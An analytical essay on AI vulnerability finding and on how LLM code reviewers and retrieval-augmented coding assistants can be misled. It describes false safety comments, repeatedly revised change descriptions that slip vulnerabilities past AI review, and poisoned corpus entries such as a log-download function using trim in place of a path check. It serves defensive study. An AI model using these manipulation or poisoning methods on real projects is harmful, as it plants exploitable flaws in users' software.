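Many planted flaws never produce the evidence that the fourth step requires. The 2003 change to the Linux kernel would not have caused a crash or memory error. Neither would Åkesson's warhead program, code that writes a password to a log, software that accepts a device without secure pairing, or a build script that leaves out a sandbox. In each case the program does what its code specifies, so a tester has to know what it should do to recognize the flaw.

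Special detectors can help with some of these flaws. The contest included command injection and path traversal, in which an attacker gets a program to open a file outside its permitted folder. A detector can treat an attempt to open such a file as a crash. A project can also write its own rules, for example that an ordinary user must still be an ordinary user after any call to the kernel's `wait4`. A model or fuzzer could then search for an input that breaks the rule. But someone has to think of the rule first, and the attacker will prefer a flaw that breaks none of the existing ones.

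A backdoor that responds only to a secret key poses a different problem, because the tester can't trigger it. In the contest, no team found either of two flaws in curl that an input could reach only after several cryptographic steps. Zhang and colleagues blame errors the models made in long calculations, and suggest giving them tools to do the arithmetic. Such tools would not have helped a tester trigger the xz backdoor, which required a digital signature made with the attacker's secret key. A model might still notice the suspicious code by reading it, but the system could not confirm the suspicion with a crash.

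If a system reports suspicions it has not confirmed, false alarms return. One part of the contest gives a rough idea of how often. The organizers sent the systems 13 warnings in the format that static analyzers use, eight genuine and five false, and asked which were which. Two teams that relied mainly on a model's judgment got 10 and 9 right, while calling every warning genuine would have got 8. The winning team, Team Atlanta, accepted a warning only if it matched a crash that its system had already produced. It accepted eight, two of them wrongly, and could never reject any, because the absence of a crash does not prove that code is sound. Thirteen warnings are too few for a reliable rate, and the models are now more than a year old.

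Newer models do find silent flaws of this kind. *Claude Finds 493 Security Issues in Open-Source Code* (Ticong, 2026) reports on a search of 25 projects with Anthropic's Claude. The findings included weaknesses that led to fixes in OpenSSH and protections that had silently stopped working, as the sandbox in xz did because of the stray dot.

### AI-found vulnerabilities in 2026

Models' scores on CyberGym, an academic benchmark for finding vulnerabilities, rose from under 20% at the start of 2025 to over 85% in 2026, according to *Launching an opt-in vulnerability-finding service for open-source software* (Anthropic, 2026). Outside benchmarks, Microsoft fixed more than 1,400 vulnerabilities in October 2026 and credited language models for the volume (Krebs, 2026, *Microsoft Patches More Than 1,400 Security Flaws*). It fixed another 1,093 in November, bringing the total for the year so far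 to more than 5,100. A year earlier, it was fixing about 100 a month (Krebs, 2026, *Microsoft Fixes Nearly 1,100 Security Vulnerabilities*).

The same has happened across the industry. Loupia (2026) reports in *Deux fois plus de failles de sécurité recensées en 2026 qu’en 2025* that the security company VulnCheck counted more than 100,000 newly recorded vulnerabilities between January and mid-November 2026, over twice as many as in all of 2025. VulnCheck believes researchers found most of them with the help of AI.

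These totals are not catch rates, because nobody knows how many vulnerabilities the models missed. They also don't include the false alarms that people had to sort through. Anthropic's Project Glasswing provides more information about those. Since April 2026 it has given selected companies and open-source developers access to Anthropic's Mythos model to search for vulnerabilities, and Anthropic reports some of its own findings to open-source projects. Cornelißen (2026), in *Glasswing*, takes these figures from Anthropic's public dashboard as of November 2:

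| Stage | Number |
| --- | --- |
| Possible vulnerabilities found | 37,966 |
| Checked by outside security companies | 6,376 |
| Reported to maintainers | 5,087 |
| Patched by maintainers | 629 |
| Marked as fixed in Anthropic's public list | 217 |

*Anthropic's Glasswing Finds Many Security Flaws Yet Delivers Few Fixes* (Poireault, 2026) describes a critical review by VulnCheck's Patrick Garrity, who measured the project by the 217 fixes. Cornelißen considers 629 the fairer number because it includes patches from maintainers who never replied to Anthropic. Even so, maintainers had patched only about one in eight of the flaws reported to them. The dashboard understates the project's results because it leaves out flaws that companies such as Microsoft fixed in their own products. Both critics have a commercial interest, since VulnCheck sells vulnerability data and Cornelißen runs a small AI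 search service.

The outside companies judged 94.2% of the findings they checked to be valid. That rate is far better than the static analyzers', but the companies checked only 17% of the candidates, and Anthropic counts duplicates and flaws that maintainers decline to fix as valid.

The share of reports confirmed as vulnerabilities was much lower for curl. VulnCheck's *After 7-months, Glasswing Overwelms Maintainers with Underwhelming Findings* (2026) reports that curl's developers had published 34 of the reports they received from Anthropic. Of the 25 they had assessed, they rejected 19 and confirmed six as low-severity vulnerabilities. They had yet to assess the other nine. VulnCheck links these reports to OSS Scanner, a service that Anthropic launched in October. Anthropic's *OSS Scanner* page explains that enrolled projects get the model's reports without waiting for a human review.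 The lack of review probably accounts for part of the gap. Some of the rejected reports may also describe real bugs that curl's developers don't consider security risks. One project isn't enough to establish the usual rate, but curl's results show that a rate measured after outside review may not predict the share of vulnerabilities among the reports a maintainer receives.

Anthropic said in October that its bottleneck was a shortage of people to validate findings. Cornelißen's service has people check every finding before reporting it. The service has reported only 120 findings, and maintainers have fixed 80% of them.

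It also matters who receives the report of a planted flaw. In the xz case, reports of errors caused by the backdoor went to the project, where the attacker answered them with a plausible excuse. A report from an AI system would have gone to the same place. A publication deadline limits how long a malicious maintainer can delay. Anthropic's *Updating our coordinated vulnerability disclosure policy timelines* (2026) shortens the company's deadline from 90 days to 30 for serious vulnerabilities and 45 for others, starting in January 2027. The company will also turn to an outside coordinator if a maintainer doesn't respond within 15 days. The new deadlines don't apply to findings that no person has reviewed, such as those from OSS Scanner.

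Anthropic says it made the change because a flaw found by one model is increasingly likely to be found by another. This makes it harder for an attacker to keep a planted flaw secret for years. But different models may also miss the same flaws, as colleagues with similar training may.

### Language models as code reviewers

A model that reviews a proposed change usually receives the author's description and the code comments along with the code. *Trusting the Tool* (2026) summarizes several studies of whether this text affects the model's verdict.

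Shahriar and colleagues took functions from PrimeVul, a collection of real code, and added information such as the author's identity or a note that an automatic analysis had found the function safe. The additions influenced all eight models in the study, changing how readily they flagged code more than how well they distinguished vulnerable code from sound code.

An invented example shows why the difference matters. Suppose a model reviews 100 vulnerable changes and 100 sound ones:

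| | Vulnerable changes flagged | Sound changes flagged |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Code alone | 70 | 30 |
| Code with a reassuring note | 50 | 15 |

The model distinguishes vulnerable changes from safe ones about equally well with and without the note. With the note, it misses 20 more vulnerable changes but raises half as many false alarms. A project that tracked only false alarms would conclude that its reviewer had improved.

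Alexopoulos and colleagues found a much larger effect when they tested review systems of the kind projects use. By repeatedly revising the descriptions of changes, they got 32 of 33 real vulnerabilities past the systems. This is a persistent attacker's success rate rather than the average effect of a reassuring description. Crude attempts sometimes made the model more likely to flag the change. *Trusting the Tool* also cites a study by Thornton that found no significant effect of misleading comments on the strongest models. Thornton used 100 samples, too few to rule out a modest effect. The two studies' results are also compatible, because a fixed set of comments is a weaker test than a description that someone keeps revising until it works.

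*When AI Agrees Too Much* (2026) points out that attackers can practice against a project's public review settings, while the reviewer has only one chance to catch the real attempt. Keeping some countermeasures secret, as Wheeler advises, would make this practice less useful.

The ALIBI study tested defenses against code comments that make false claims about safety, including invented reports from other tools. Hiding unverifiable comments from the model worked better than telling it to distrust them.

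Removing all comments and descriptions also removes some facts that a reviewer needs. A model has no basis for flagging code that skips secure pairing if its input doesn't include the requirement that a device pair securely before it connects. A project could have the model review the code alone first, then again with the description, and ask a person to look whenever the second verdict is more favorable. This would take twice as much computing but would keep the useful information.

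*Trusting the Tool* cites research in which models that correctly called code vulnerable often gave invented or unverifiable reasons. A maintainer who finds that the reason is wrong may dismiss the warning, even though the code is flawed.

### Finding a bug and recognizing a disguise

Unlike entries to the Underhanded C Contest, the flaws planted in the AI Cyber Challenge were mostly not disguised. In three of the C projects, the organizers chose flaws that were easy to find because they wanted to test patching and the sorting of duplicates. A few of the 63 flaws were backdoors. Three of these were labeled "flag", a convention from hacking contests, and a programmer could repair them by deleting the labeled code. Another, in Java, was deliberately hard to read, and no team patched it.

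Whether a flaw was planted or accidental sometimes makes little difference to detection. A model that notices when a programmer has forgotten a length check should also notice when someone has left one out on purpose, if the surrounding code is equally clear. The progress of 2026 should therefore make it harder for attackers to hide ordinary memory errors, including use-after-free flaws like those in the Minnesota patches.

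Attackers can run the available models on draft code, as they can check it for compiler warnings, and keep only a flaw that the models miss. The contest made this easier by requiring finalists to publish their systems, as the winning team's paper, *ATLANTIS* (2025), mentions. A model is therefore likely to find a larger share of accidental flaws than of flaws planted by someone who has prepared for it. The attacker's advantage may not last, because attackers can test a flaw only against the models available at the time, while defenders can rescan the project's code with every new model.

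Finding a planted flaw also doesn't reveal that someone planted it. Some of the vulnerabilities recorded in 2026 could have been deliberate. To find out, a project would have to look up who introduced each flaw and check that person's other changes, which is a lot of work for thousands of reports.

Researchers could measure how well models recognize disguised code by mixing disguised programs with honest ones, as in a fair test of human reviewers. The disguised programs would have to be new, because models may have been trained on the published explanations of the contest entries. The test should also let the authors revise their programs against one model before other models review them.

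## Experiments on poisoned code examples in retrieval corpora

Language models that can find vulnerabilities also copy them, so a coding assistant that retrieves a flawed example often writes new code with the same flaw. Two studies measured how often this happens when an attacker chooses the example. Both found large effects, but they used mostly small or older models, relied on AI judges and assumed that nobody had checked the corpus entries. In experiments from November 2026, current models also copied flaws from code they were shown, but none of these experiments simulated an attack on a retrieval corpus.

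### From request to generated code

Retrieval-augmented code generation means giving a language model relevant examples along with the request. A typical system works like this:

1. A developer describes the code they want. This description is the query.
2. A search program, the retriever, compares the query with the entries in the corpus and picks out candidates. A keyword retriever looks for shared words. A dense retriever uses a neural network to turn each text into a long list of numbers, or vector, so that texts with similar meanings get vectors that point in similar directions. It then scores each entry by the cosine of the angle between its vector and the query's, which is 1 if they point the same way.
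3. In some systems a second model, the re-ranker, reads the query together with each candidate and puts the candidates in a better order.
4. The system puts the best few entries into the prompt with the query.
5. The language model reads the prompt and writes the code.

None of these steps checks whether an entry is safe. Suppose the corpus has two versions of a function that opens a log file, and only one of them checks the file name. They do the same job and share nearly all their words, so the retriever gives them almost the same score.

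### One vulnerable example per request

Lin, Chen and colleagues (2025), in *Exploring the Security Threats of Knowledge Base Poisoning in Retrieval-Augmented Code Generation*, built a corpus from 12,053 C, C++, Java and Python functions that had once contained a real vulnerability. They used the repaired version of each function in the clean corpus and the version from before the repair as the pool of code for the attacker. They used a short description of what each function does as the query.

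In the main scenario the attacker knows the query and adds the vulnerable functions that match it best. The retriever then passes one example to the model. The table shows the percentage of generated functions that the study's AI judge found vulnerable, by the number of poisoned examples added for each query:

| Model | Dense retriever: 0 | 1 | 9 | Keyword retriever: 0 | 1 | 9 |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
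| GPT-4o | 26 | 42 | 47 | 27 | 30 | 33 |
| Llama 3 8B | 18 | 34 | 37 | 22 | 28 | 33 |
| Code Llama 13B | 29 | 48 | 53 | 27 | 33 | 37 |
| DeepSeek-Coder-V2 16B | 25 | 44 | 50 | 28 | 33 | 35 |

Lin and colleagues report that a single poisoned example can make about 48% of the generated code vulnerable. But 29% of Code Llama's output was already vulnerable with a clean corpus, so the poisoning added 19 percentage points. They also used one poisoned example per request and picked new examples for every query. The 48% is therefore the rate across thousands of separate attacks, each aimed at one known request, rather than the effect of one poisoned example on everything an assistant writes.

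The two retrievers differ so much because the dense one is more accurate. It ranked the matching function first for 79% of queries, compared with 14% for the keyword retriever. It therefore also found the attacker's example more often. When the attacker had added one, the dense retriever put it into 38% of prompts and the keyword retriever into 5%. Since Code Llama's vulnerable share rose by 19 points with the dense retriever, about half of the prompts with a poisoned example seem to have led the model to write vulnerable code instead of sound code.

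With the keyword retriever and nine poisoned examples per query, only 7% of prompts contained a poisoned example, yet the vulnerable share of Llama 3's code rose by 11 points. The other 93% of prompts should have been unchanged, so part of the rise must have another cause, such as random variation in the model's or the judge's answers. Differences of a few points in this study are therefore unreliable. The rises of 16 to 19 points with the dense retriever are too large to explain this way.

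An attacker who doesn't know the queries has a much harder task. To test this case, Lin and colleagues added vulnerable code resembling the most typical functions in the corpus. With about 2,400 such entries, equal to 20% of the corpus, the vulnerable share of Code Llama's generated code rose from 29% to 36%, and GPT-4o's rose from 26% to 32%. The attacker would have had to add more than 9,600 entries to get poisoned examples into prompts as often as one targeted example did. A few poisoned entries are enough only when the attacker can predict the requests, perhaps from a project's public plans or code review discussions.

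### How reliable the AI judge was

The researchers used another language model, DeepSeek-V2.5, to judge whether generated code was vulnerable. They rejected static analysis because the models wrote isolated functions that are hard to compile. They gave DeepSeek-V2.5 a description of a known flaw and its repair, and used it to check whether the new code contained that flaw. The paper's text reports the judge's accuracy as 77% to 81%, while the detailed results of the manual check range from 72% for C++ to 84% for Python.

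Errors at this rate can distort the results considerably. Suppose the judge correctly classifies 80% of vulnerable code and 80% of sound code. If 15% of the code is vulnerable, the judge will flag 29%, because its false alarms outnumber the flaws it misses. If 47% is vulnerable, it will flag 48%. Code Llama's baseline could therefore be much lower than reported, and the effect of poisoning larger.

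The judge may also have been biased in the opposite direction, inflating the results for the poisoned corpus. It always checked for the flaw that the requested function had once contained, and when the prompt included a poisoned example, it checked for that example's flaw as well. If the two flaws were different, the judge had an extra chance to raise a false alarm. The manual check covered only code generated from a poisoned corpus, so it can't show which bias was larger.

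### CodePoisonRAG

The attacker in that study could use only vulnerable functions that already existed. Gadey, Marey and Dmitrienko (2026), in *CodePoisonRAG*, tested entries written for the attack, each aimed at one expected request and one chosen type of flaw. They added 85 entries (65 in Java and 20 in C) to a clean corpus of 12,053 functions, so 0.7% of the total was poisoned. The entries covered ten types of weakness, including SQL injection, path traversal and buffer overflow.

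The system put the top three results for each request into the prompt. All 85 poisoned entries ranked in the top three, both before and after the researchers reworded the requests. This is less surprising given that each request described the function in its poisoned entry.

An attack counted as a success if the model received the entry and an AI judge found the chosen flaw in the generated code. The researchers also repeated the test with CodeGuarder, a defense that adds security advice to the prompt:

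| Model | No defense | With CodeGuarder |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Qwen 3.5 9B | 68 of 85 (80%) | 34 of 85 (40%) |
| Code Llama 13B | 79 of 85 (93%) | 60 of 85 (71%) |
| DeepSeek-Coder-V2 16B | 68 of 85 (80%) | 51 of 85 (60%) |

To find out how much of this was due to the poisoning, Gadey and colleagues ran Code Llama again with sound functions in place of the poisoned ones. It still produced the flaw for 25 of the 85 requests (29%), so poisoning added 54 cases, or 64 percentage points. The increase varied by type of flaw. Code injection, in which the program runs text from an outsider as code, rose from 1 in 10 to 10 in 10. Unsafe deserialization, in which a program rebuilds objects from data supplied by an outsider, rose only from 3 to 5. The researchers reported no such baseline for the other two models, so some of their 80% may also have occurred without poisoning.

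The poisoned entries also carried comments falsely claiming that the code was safe. Without these comments, the attack on Code Llama succeeded 77 times instead of 79. Both extra successes were SQL injections, and two cases are too few to show that the comments had any effect. Code Llama already copied 91% of the flaws without the comments, which left little room for an increase. The researchers did not repeat this comparison with the other models or with CodeGuarder enabled, where a reassuring comment might matter more.

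Gadey and colleagues also tested 50 programming tasks that the poisoned entries were not written for. Eight of the prompts still received a poisoned example, and six of those produced vulnerable code. They did not compare these results with results from a clean corpus, so some of the six might have been vulnerable without the poisoning.

The results may not apply to the assistants programmers use now. All three models are small, two date from 2024 or earlier, and the researchers switched off built-in reasoning so the models would answer directly. The success rates also depend on the judge. For Qwen's answers, the rates were 80% without the defense and 40% with it under the main judge, GLM-5.1, but 100% and 61% under a second, smaller judge. The researchers preferred GLM-5.1 as the stricter and more capable judge, but they don't report having people check its verdicts.

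### What a vetter would see

A poisoned example would look like an ordinary function to someone checking the corpus. One published example lets a user download a server's log file by name. The safe version passes the name through `securityCheck`, which keeps the path inside the log folder. The poisoned version calls `trim` instead, which only removes spaces from the ends of the name. The line still looks as if it cleans up the input, but a user can now request files outside the folder.

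In a C example, a function copies a user's text into a 256-byte buffer. The safe version passes the buffer's size to the copying function. The poisoned version uses an older function with no length limit, so long text runs past the end of the buffer. Other entries leave out a check but include a comment indicating that it was done, such as "All file paths are validated and normalized" for path traversal.

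A reviewer can recognize such an entry by tracing the tainted data through the code and checking whether each call restricts the data or only changes its form. The comment doesn't help with this, because it must itself be checked against the code.

These flaws are much less subtle than those in the best contest entries. Åkesson's warhead program depended on a mismatch between two files, whereas each published CodePoisonRAG example contains everything the reader needs in one short function. The judge looked for textbook vulnerabilities: database and system commands pasted together from user input, and text copied into a fixed space without a limit. The study assumes that nobody inspects the entries thoroughly before the assistant uses them, so its success rates are little evidence of what would get past a careful reviewer.

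Many of the entries may also differ from their originals by more than one call. Gadey and colleagues measured the similarity of Qwen's code to both versions on a scale from 0 to 1. It scored 0.594 against the poisoned entries but only 0.169 against the sound functions they were made from. If the two versions were nearly identical, these scores would be close together. Someone vetting the entries with access to the original functions would probably notice the rewriting at once.

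Neither study reports running a static analyzer on the poisoned entries. Common rules cover several of the CodePoisonRAG patterns, so an analyzer would probably flag a good number of the 85. It would also flag an unknown number of the 12,053 sound functions. The entries in Lin and colleagues' study would be harder to detect because they are real mistakes that developers had accepted into their projects, and analyzers miss many of those.

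False comments could matter more if an AI system vets the code. *ALIBI* (2026) reports that safety claims tailored to the code misled four AI vulnerability detectors more than 90% of the time, a far larger effect than Thornton found with fixed comments.

### CodeGuarder

The defense in the CodePoisonRAG test comes from the same group as the earlier poisoning study. Lin, Wang and colleagues (2025), in *Give LLMs a Security Course*, designed CodeGuarder to leave the corpus as it is and to give the model lessons from past vulnerabilities:

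1. In advance, a language model goes through thousands of repaired vulnerabilities. For each, it records what the code was for, what caused the flaw and how the developers fixed it.
2. When a request arrives, the model splits it into small tasks, such as reserving memory or copying a piece of text.
3. A retriever finds the lessons that best match each task.
4. CodeGuarder ranks the tasks by how often language models make the mistakes in those lessons, and keeps the five riskiest.
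5. It adds these tasks and their lessons to the prompt, next to the ordinary code examples.

The researchers tested it on four models, among them GPT-4o and DeepSeek-V3. On average, this share of the generated code was secure:

| Corpus | Without CodeGuarder | With CodeGuarder |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Clean | 60.8% | 73.1% |
| Poisoned by an attacker who knows the request | 50.6% | 66.5% |
| Poisoned by an attacker who doesn't | 60.1% | 73.2% |

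The paper describes the middle row as a 31.5% improvement, which is relative to the starting value and equals 16 percentage points. Most of that gain has little to do with poisoning, since CodeGuarder also adds 12 points when the corpus is clean. With the defense in place, an attacker who knows the request still lowers the secure share by almost 7 points, compared with 10 without it.

CodeGuarder helps far more with some flaws than others. With DeepSeek-V3, it prevented 89% of one class of memory errors but only 8% of path traversal flaws and 5% of cross-site scripting flaws, in which a website passes an attacker's code on to other visitors. The cross-site scripting figure is based on just 13 cases. One possible reason for the gap is the ranking in step 4, which gives high weights to memory errors and a minimal weight to both of these web flaws. But SQL injection gets the same minimal weight,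 and CodeGuarder prevented 36% of those flaws.

How well CodeGuarder works also depends on the model. In the CodePoisonRAG test, Code Llama with CodeGuarder still reproduced 8 of 10 path traversal flaws and 9 of 10 cross-site scripting flaws, while Qwen, a newer model, reproduced 2 and 1. CodeGuarder probably had an advantage in that test because its lessons came from the same collection of repaired functions as the poisoned entries. Lin and colleagues avoided such an overlap in their own test of CodeGuarder by taking the poisoned examples from a different collection.

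The researchers measured security with the rule-based detector from their benchmark, CyberSecEval. Of the flaws it reports, 96% are real, so it is less prone to false alarms than an AI judge. The poisoned examples also came from CyberSecEval, and the detector's rules were written for that benchmark. Running the detector on the corpus beforehand would probably have exposed many of the poisoned examples, but the researchers don't report trying this.

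CodeGuarder showed a smaller benefit in a stricter test. In *A.S.E 2.0*, Yu, Fan and colleagues (2026) had six models, including GPT-5.4, fill in missing code in 51 real projects. They counted an answer as secure only if it passed tests of its normal functions and resisted a working exploit. With a rebuilt version of CodeGuarder, the share of secure answers rose from 12.6% to 16.8%, but the difference was not statistically significant. Nobody had poisoned the projects, so the result does not directly measure how well the defense works under attack. CodeGuarder ranked higher among the compared methods when the researchers judged the same code by static analysis, but they warn that such analysis can favor code that merely contains defensive patterns.

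Even a corpus that nobody has attacked may contain insecure code. While preparing their clean corpus, Lin and colleagues found 841 Java functions that generate random numbers in CodeSearchNet, a widely used collection of open-source code. Of these, 684 used a weak method, which is dangerous if the numbers serve as keys or passwords.

### Tests on current models

*Coding Agents Propagate Vulnerabilities in Code Bases* (Sun, Mündler-Sasahara et al., 2026) comes closest to repeating these experiments with current models. The researchers tested coding agents, which search a project and open files on their own, and varied only the security of the existing code. They did not test deliberately poisoned retrieval examples, but expect these to work by the same mechanism.

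In one experiment, agents filled in a missing piece of a real C or C++ project at a spot where a memory error had once occurred. Similar code elsewhere in the project either had the necessary check or lacked it. The researchers then ran an input known to trigger the old error. All five models did worse when the similar code was insecure:

- On average, the share of secure answers was 35 percentage points lower.
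- The difference ranged from 25 points to 49.
- GPT-5.6 Sol had the largest drop, from 91% to 42%.

The experiment used only 20 pairs of tasks, from five projects. It also had no neutral version, because the agents needed the surrounding code to complete the tasks. Part of the gap may therefore come from good examples helping rather than from bad ones doing harm.

Another experiment did have a neutral version. Agents wrote a new web application in a folder that was empty or contained up to five existing applications, none of which they needed for the task. Insecure existing applications lowered the share of new applications that were both correct and secure by 3.4 percentage points on average, and secure ones raised it by 4.4. A poisoned retrieval example also comes from an unrelated program, but the retrieval system puts it directly into the prompt, whereas an agent can ignore the other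 applications in a folder. Its effect on the same models could therefore be well above 3.4 points.

In 74 of Yu and colleagues' tasks, the project contained other code with the same weakness. For these tasks, they gave three models the relevant security checks from the project, then added one of the insecure examples directly to the prompt. The share of answers that worked but were open to attack rose by 6.3 percentage points. Irrelevant code of the same length raised it by only 0.6 points, so the models were responding to the content of the example and not just to a longer prompt.

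This is far below the 64 points in the CodePoisonRAG test, but here the prompt still contained the correct checks, and nobody had written the insecure example to match the request. The models also had less room to get worse, because with only the current file as context, 44% of their answers already worked but were vulnerable.

A sound example can also make new code safer. In one of Yu and colleagues' tasks, the model had to write the part of an image library that reads a GIF file's dimensions. A width of zero makes the program divide by zero. The library's reader for Targa, another image format, checks for this. When the prompt included that reader, GPT-5.4 copied the check in every run. When the prompt instead included any of four other selections of code from the library, GPT-5.4 omitted the check every time, and the program passed its ordinary tests but failed on a GIF with zero width.

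Simple instructions can reduce the copying of flaws but don't reliably stop it. Sun and colleagues told agents to be careful not to bring in bugs from existing code. In the web experiment, this removed the harm from nearby insecure code for Claude Opus 5, reduced it for GLM 5.3 and made no difference for GPT-5.6 Sol. Telling agents to follow the existing style, a common request in real projects, doubled the harm for GLM 5.3, from 4.5 points to 9.

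The agents often knew enough to avoid these mistakes. When the researchers showed them their own vulnerable C and C++ code and asked whether it had bugs, the agents identified the flaw in about 70% of cases. When asked instead why they had written it that way, they said in 77% of cases that they had followed similar code elsewhere in the project.

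## What the cases imply for finding poisoned examples

The poisoning experiments assumed that nobody inspects the corpus closely. An inspector would have less information than a maintainer reviewing a patch, and would get many false alarms because poisoned entries are rare. Researchers have tested few of the obvious checks on retrieval corpora, so support for most of them is inferred from work on patches, releases and single functions.

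### What a corpus entry lacks

| A proposed change usually comes with | How that helped in earlier cases | A corpus entry often has |
| --- | --- | --- |
| An older version to compare it with | BitMover found the 2003 kernel edit by comparing two copies | One version |
| A named author | Kernel developers could recheck the Minnesota group's 435 commits | No author, or the wrong one |
| A program that people test and run | Valgrind errors were the first sign of the xz backdoor | Nothing that runs |
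| The surrounding code | The MDIO flaw is visible only to someone who looks up what the caller does | A single function |
| Someone whose job is to read it | Dan Carpenter answered the RapidIO patch within hours | No reader before the assistant retrieves it |

A diff between the safe and poisoned versions of the log-download function from CodePoisonRAG would show that a call to `securityCheck` had been removed, and most reviewers would ask why. In the corpus, the poisoned version appears without that diff, as a function that calls `trim`.

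Not knowing who wrote a poisoned example matters most after someone finds it. Kernel developers who distrusted one patch knew to recheck others from the same source, but finding one bad corpus entry of unknown origin doesn't help identify others. And if nobody is responsible for the entries, a warning about one may not reach anyone who can act on it.

### Judging a function by itself

The greatest difficulty is judging a function without the rest of its program. In *Top Score on the Wrong Exam*, Risse, Liu and Böhme (2024) examined 300 functions that popular research datasets label as vulnerable. Two security researchers spent more than 150 hours on them and confirmed 151 as the source of a vulnerability. Judging any of the 151 required information from outside the function. One, from the machine-learning library TensorFlow, divides by `num_splits` and crashes if it is zero, but the function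 doesn't show whether any caller can pass zero. Context also matters for sound functions, since 82 of 90 would be unsafe in some other program.

This standard is strict, because it is always possible that a caller has already made the necessary check. *Graph Is the Verifier* (Li, Zhang et al., 2026) used an AI judge to assess 138 vulnerable functions and reported a lower figure, with 99 of them (72%) needing evidence from outside the function. The missing fact was most often in a function that the vulnerable one calls.

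Some poisoned entries are easier to judge. The log-download function takes a file name straight from a web request, and `trim` is a standard Java function, so a reader can tell the code is unsafe. The safe version is harder to verify because `securityCheck` is defined elsewhere and might not work.

Automatic tools have trouble with isolated functions for related reasons:

- **Compiling.** A function usually refers to types and other functions that the entry doesn't include. The C example from CodePoisonRAG calls `write_log`, which belongs to the original program, so a compiler can't build a working program from the entry.
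- **Static analysis.** Pattern rules still work, and one against `sprintf` would flag that C example. Taint tracking needs a source. If the data arrives as an ordinary argument, the tool has to guess whether an outsider controls it. Treating every argument as untrusted causes false alarms, and trusting them all causes misses.
- **Fuzzing.** Someone has to write a harness that replaces the missing functions and chooses the inputs. A crash may then show only that the harness passed a value no real caller would, such as zero splits.

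Good benchmark scores are weak evidence that a detector can find poisoned code. Risse and colleagues trained a simple classifier on only word counts, and it scored about as well as specialized vulnerability detectors. But a poisoned function can share most of its words with a sound one. When Li and colleagues showed Claude Opus 4.7 the vulnerable and repaired versions of the same functions, it judged both correctly in 27% of pairs, compared with 25% expected from random guessing. A small model that they trained to look up callers and other facts in the project reached 38%. The vulnerabilities in this test were real mistakes, often subtler than the textbook flaws in CodePoisonRAG, and stronger models have since been released.

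*Beyond Function-Level Analysis* (2026) found that adding more code as context does not effectively solve the problem by itself, so a model must also identify which outside fact matters.

Another approach is to describe the conditions under which code would be unsafe instead of giving a yes-or-no verdict, as the system in *LLM-based Code Auditing by Inferring and Evaluating Developer Assumptions* (2026) does for functions. A corpus owner could store such a condition with the entry, for example that the caller must rule out zero splits, and the assistant could check it whenever it uses the entry. Nobody appears to have tried this on a retrieval corpus. The paper measures effort as the average number of findings someone examines before confirming one known flaw. In a corpus, that number depends heavily on how rare the poisoned entries are.

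### How many alarms would be right

Gadey and colleagues hid 85 poisoned entries among 12,053 clean ones. Suppose a scanner flags half of the poisoned entries and 5% of the clean ones. It would produce about 43 true alarms and 603 false ones, so only one alarm in 15 would be right. The table compares this scanner with some alternatives, all with invented rates:

| Method | Poisoned entries flagged | Clean entries flagged | Alarms that are right |
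| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Scanner that flags 50% of poisoned and 5% of clean entries | 43 | 603 | 1 in 15 |
| Stronger scanner: 90% and 1% | 77 | 121 | 2 in 5 |
| Two unrelated checks, each 50% and 5%, where both must flag the entry | 21 | 30 | 2 in 5 |
| The same two checks, where either is enough | 64 | 1,175 | 1 in 19 |

Before any check, the odds that an entry is poisoned are 85 to 12,053, or about 1 to 142. An alarm multiplies those odds by the scanner's catch rate divided by its false-alarm rate. For the first scanner, that ratio is 50% to 5%, or 10, which raises the odds to about 1 to 14, so about one alarm in 15 is correct. Reducing false alarms helps more than catching more poisoned entries. If the first scanner caught 90% of them instead of 50%, one alarm in nine would be correct. If it instead cut its false-alarm rate from 5% to 1%, one alarm in four would be correct.

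A second check multiplies the odds by ten again only if its mistakes are independent of the first scanner's. If it confirms half of the first scanner's alarms, true and false alike, 21 true alarms and about 300 false ones remain, so still only one alarm in 15 is true. Requiring two alarms also misses 64 of the 85 poisoned entries.

Showing one tool's verdict to the next can easily compromise this independence. *Trusting the Tool* gave language models C and C++ functions with notes from a static analyzer, some of them false. A false note that a missing check was present lowered detection of real vulnerabilities by up to 19 percentage points. False warnings never significantly lowered accuracy, because the models tended to look for the supposedly missing check and find it. A second model vetting a corpus should therefore not be shown which entries the first model called safe.

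The 5% false-alarm rate may be too low. Li and colleagues tested their model on a set with 16 sound functions for every vulnerable one. It caught 67% of the vulnerable functions, but only 11% of its alarms were right, compared with 66% when vulnerable and sound functions were equally common. These figures imply that it flagged about a third of the sound functions. At the same rates, it would raise about 57 true alarms and 3,900 false ones on the CodePoisonRAG corpus, so about one alarm in 70 would be right. Textbook flaws might be easier to tell from sound code, but the model also relied on being able to search the whole project.

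There could also be far fewer poisoned entries, since an attacker interested in one request needs only one. The first scanner would then still give 603 false alarms and have an even chance of flagging the poisoned entry.

### Checking the text of an entry

Telling human reviewers to look for security flaws greatly improved their results in experiments. Language models also respond to such wording, but without becoming more accurate. In *Words Speak Louder Than Code*, Shahriar, Cai and colleagues (2026) compared, for example, asking models to verify that code meets security standards with asking them to identify threats. The wording had a larger effect than the identity of the code's author or an earlier verdict, but correct detections and false alarms rose or fell by similar amounts. Models often changed their answer from safe to vulnerable without identifying the flaw.

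This would be a bad trade in a corpus, because a rise of ten percentage points in both rates would catch eight or nine more of the 85 poisoned entries but add about 1,200 false alarms. A vetter could require the model to name the untrusted input, the dangerous operation and the missing check before counting its answer as an alarm. That should remove some unfounded alarms, but this is an inference from the results, and the study did not test it.

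The ALIBI results suggest hiding comments from a model that vets entries. Deleting comments from the corpus would do little to protect the assistant, because the CodePoisonRAG attack worked almost as well without false comments. *Black-Box Adversarial Attacks on LLM-Based Code Completion* (2024) suggests that deleting all comments may also reduce performance on ordinary tasks, because code models rely on them, but it does not measure the loss. A corpus owner can avoid this problem by keeping the comments in the stored entries and hiding them only from the vetting model.

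Checking comments such as "All file paths are validated and normalized" against the code could also help find poisoned examples. The most successful remedy in *Trusting the Tool* was to check each of the analyzer's notes against the code in a separate request, then show the auditing model which notes were false. In a test on 300 new pairs of functions, this raised one model's accuracy by 12 percentage points when it was given false reassurances. A second model gained about half as much, which was not statistically significant. However, the study tested notes from a tool, not comments in a corpus.

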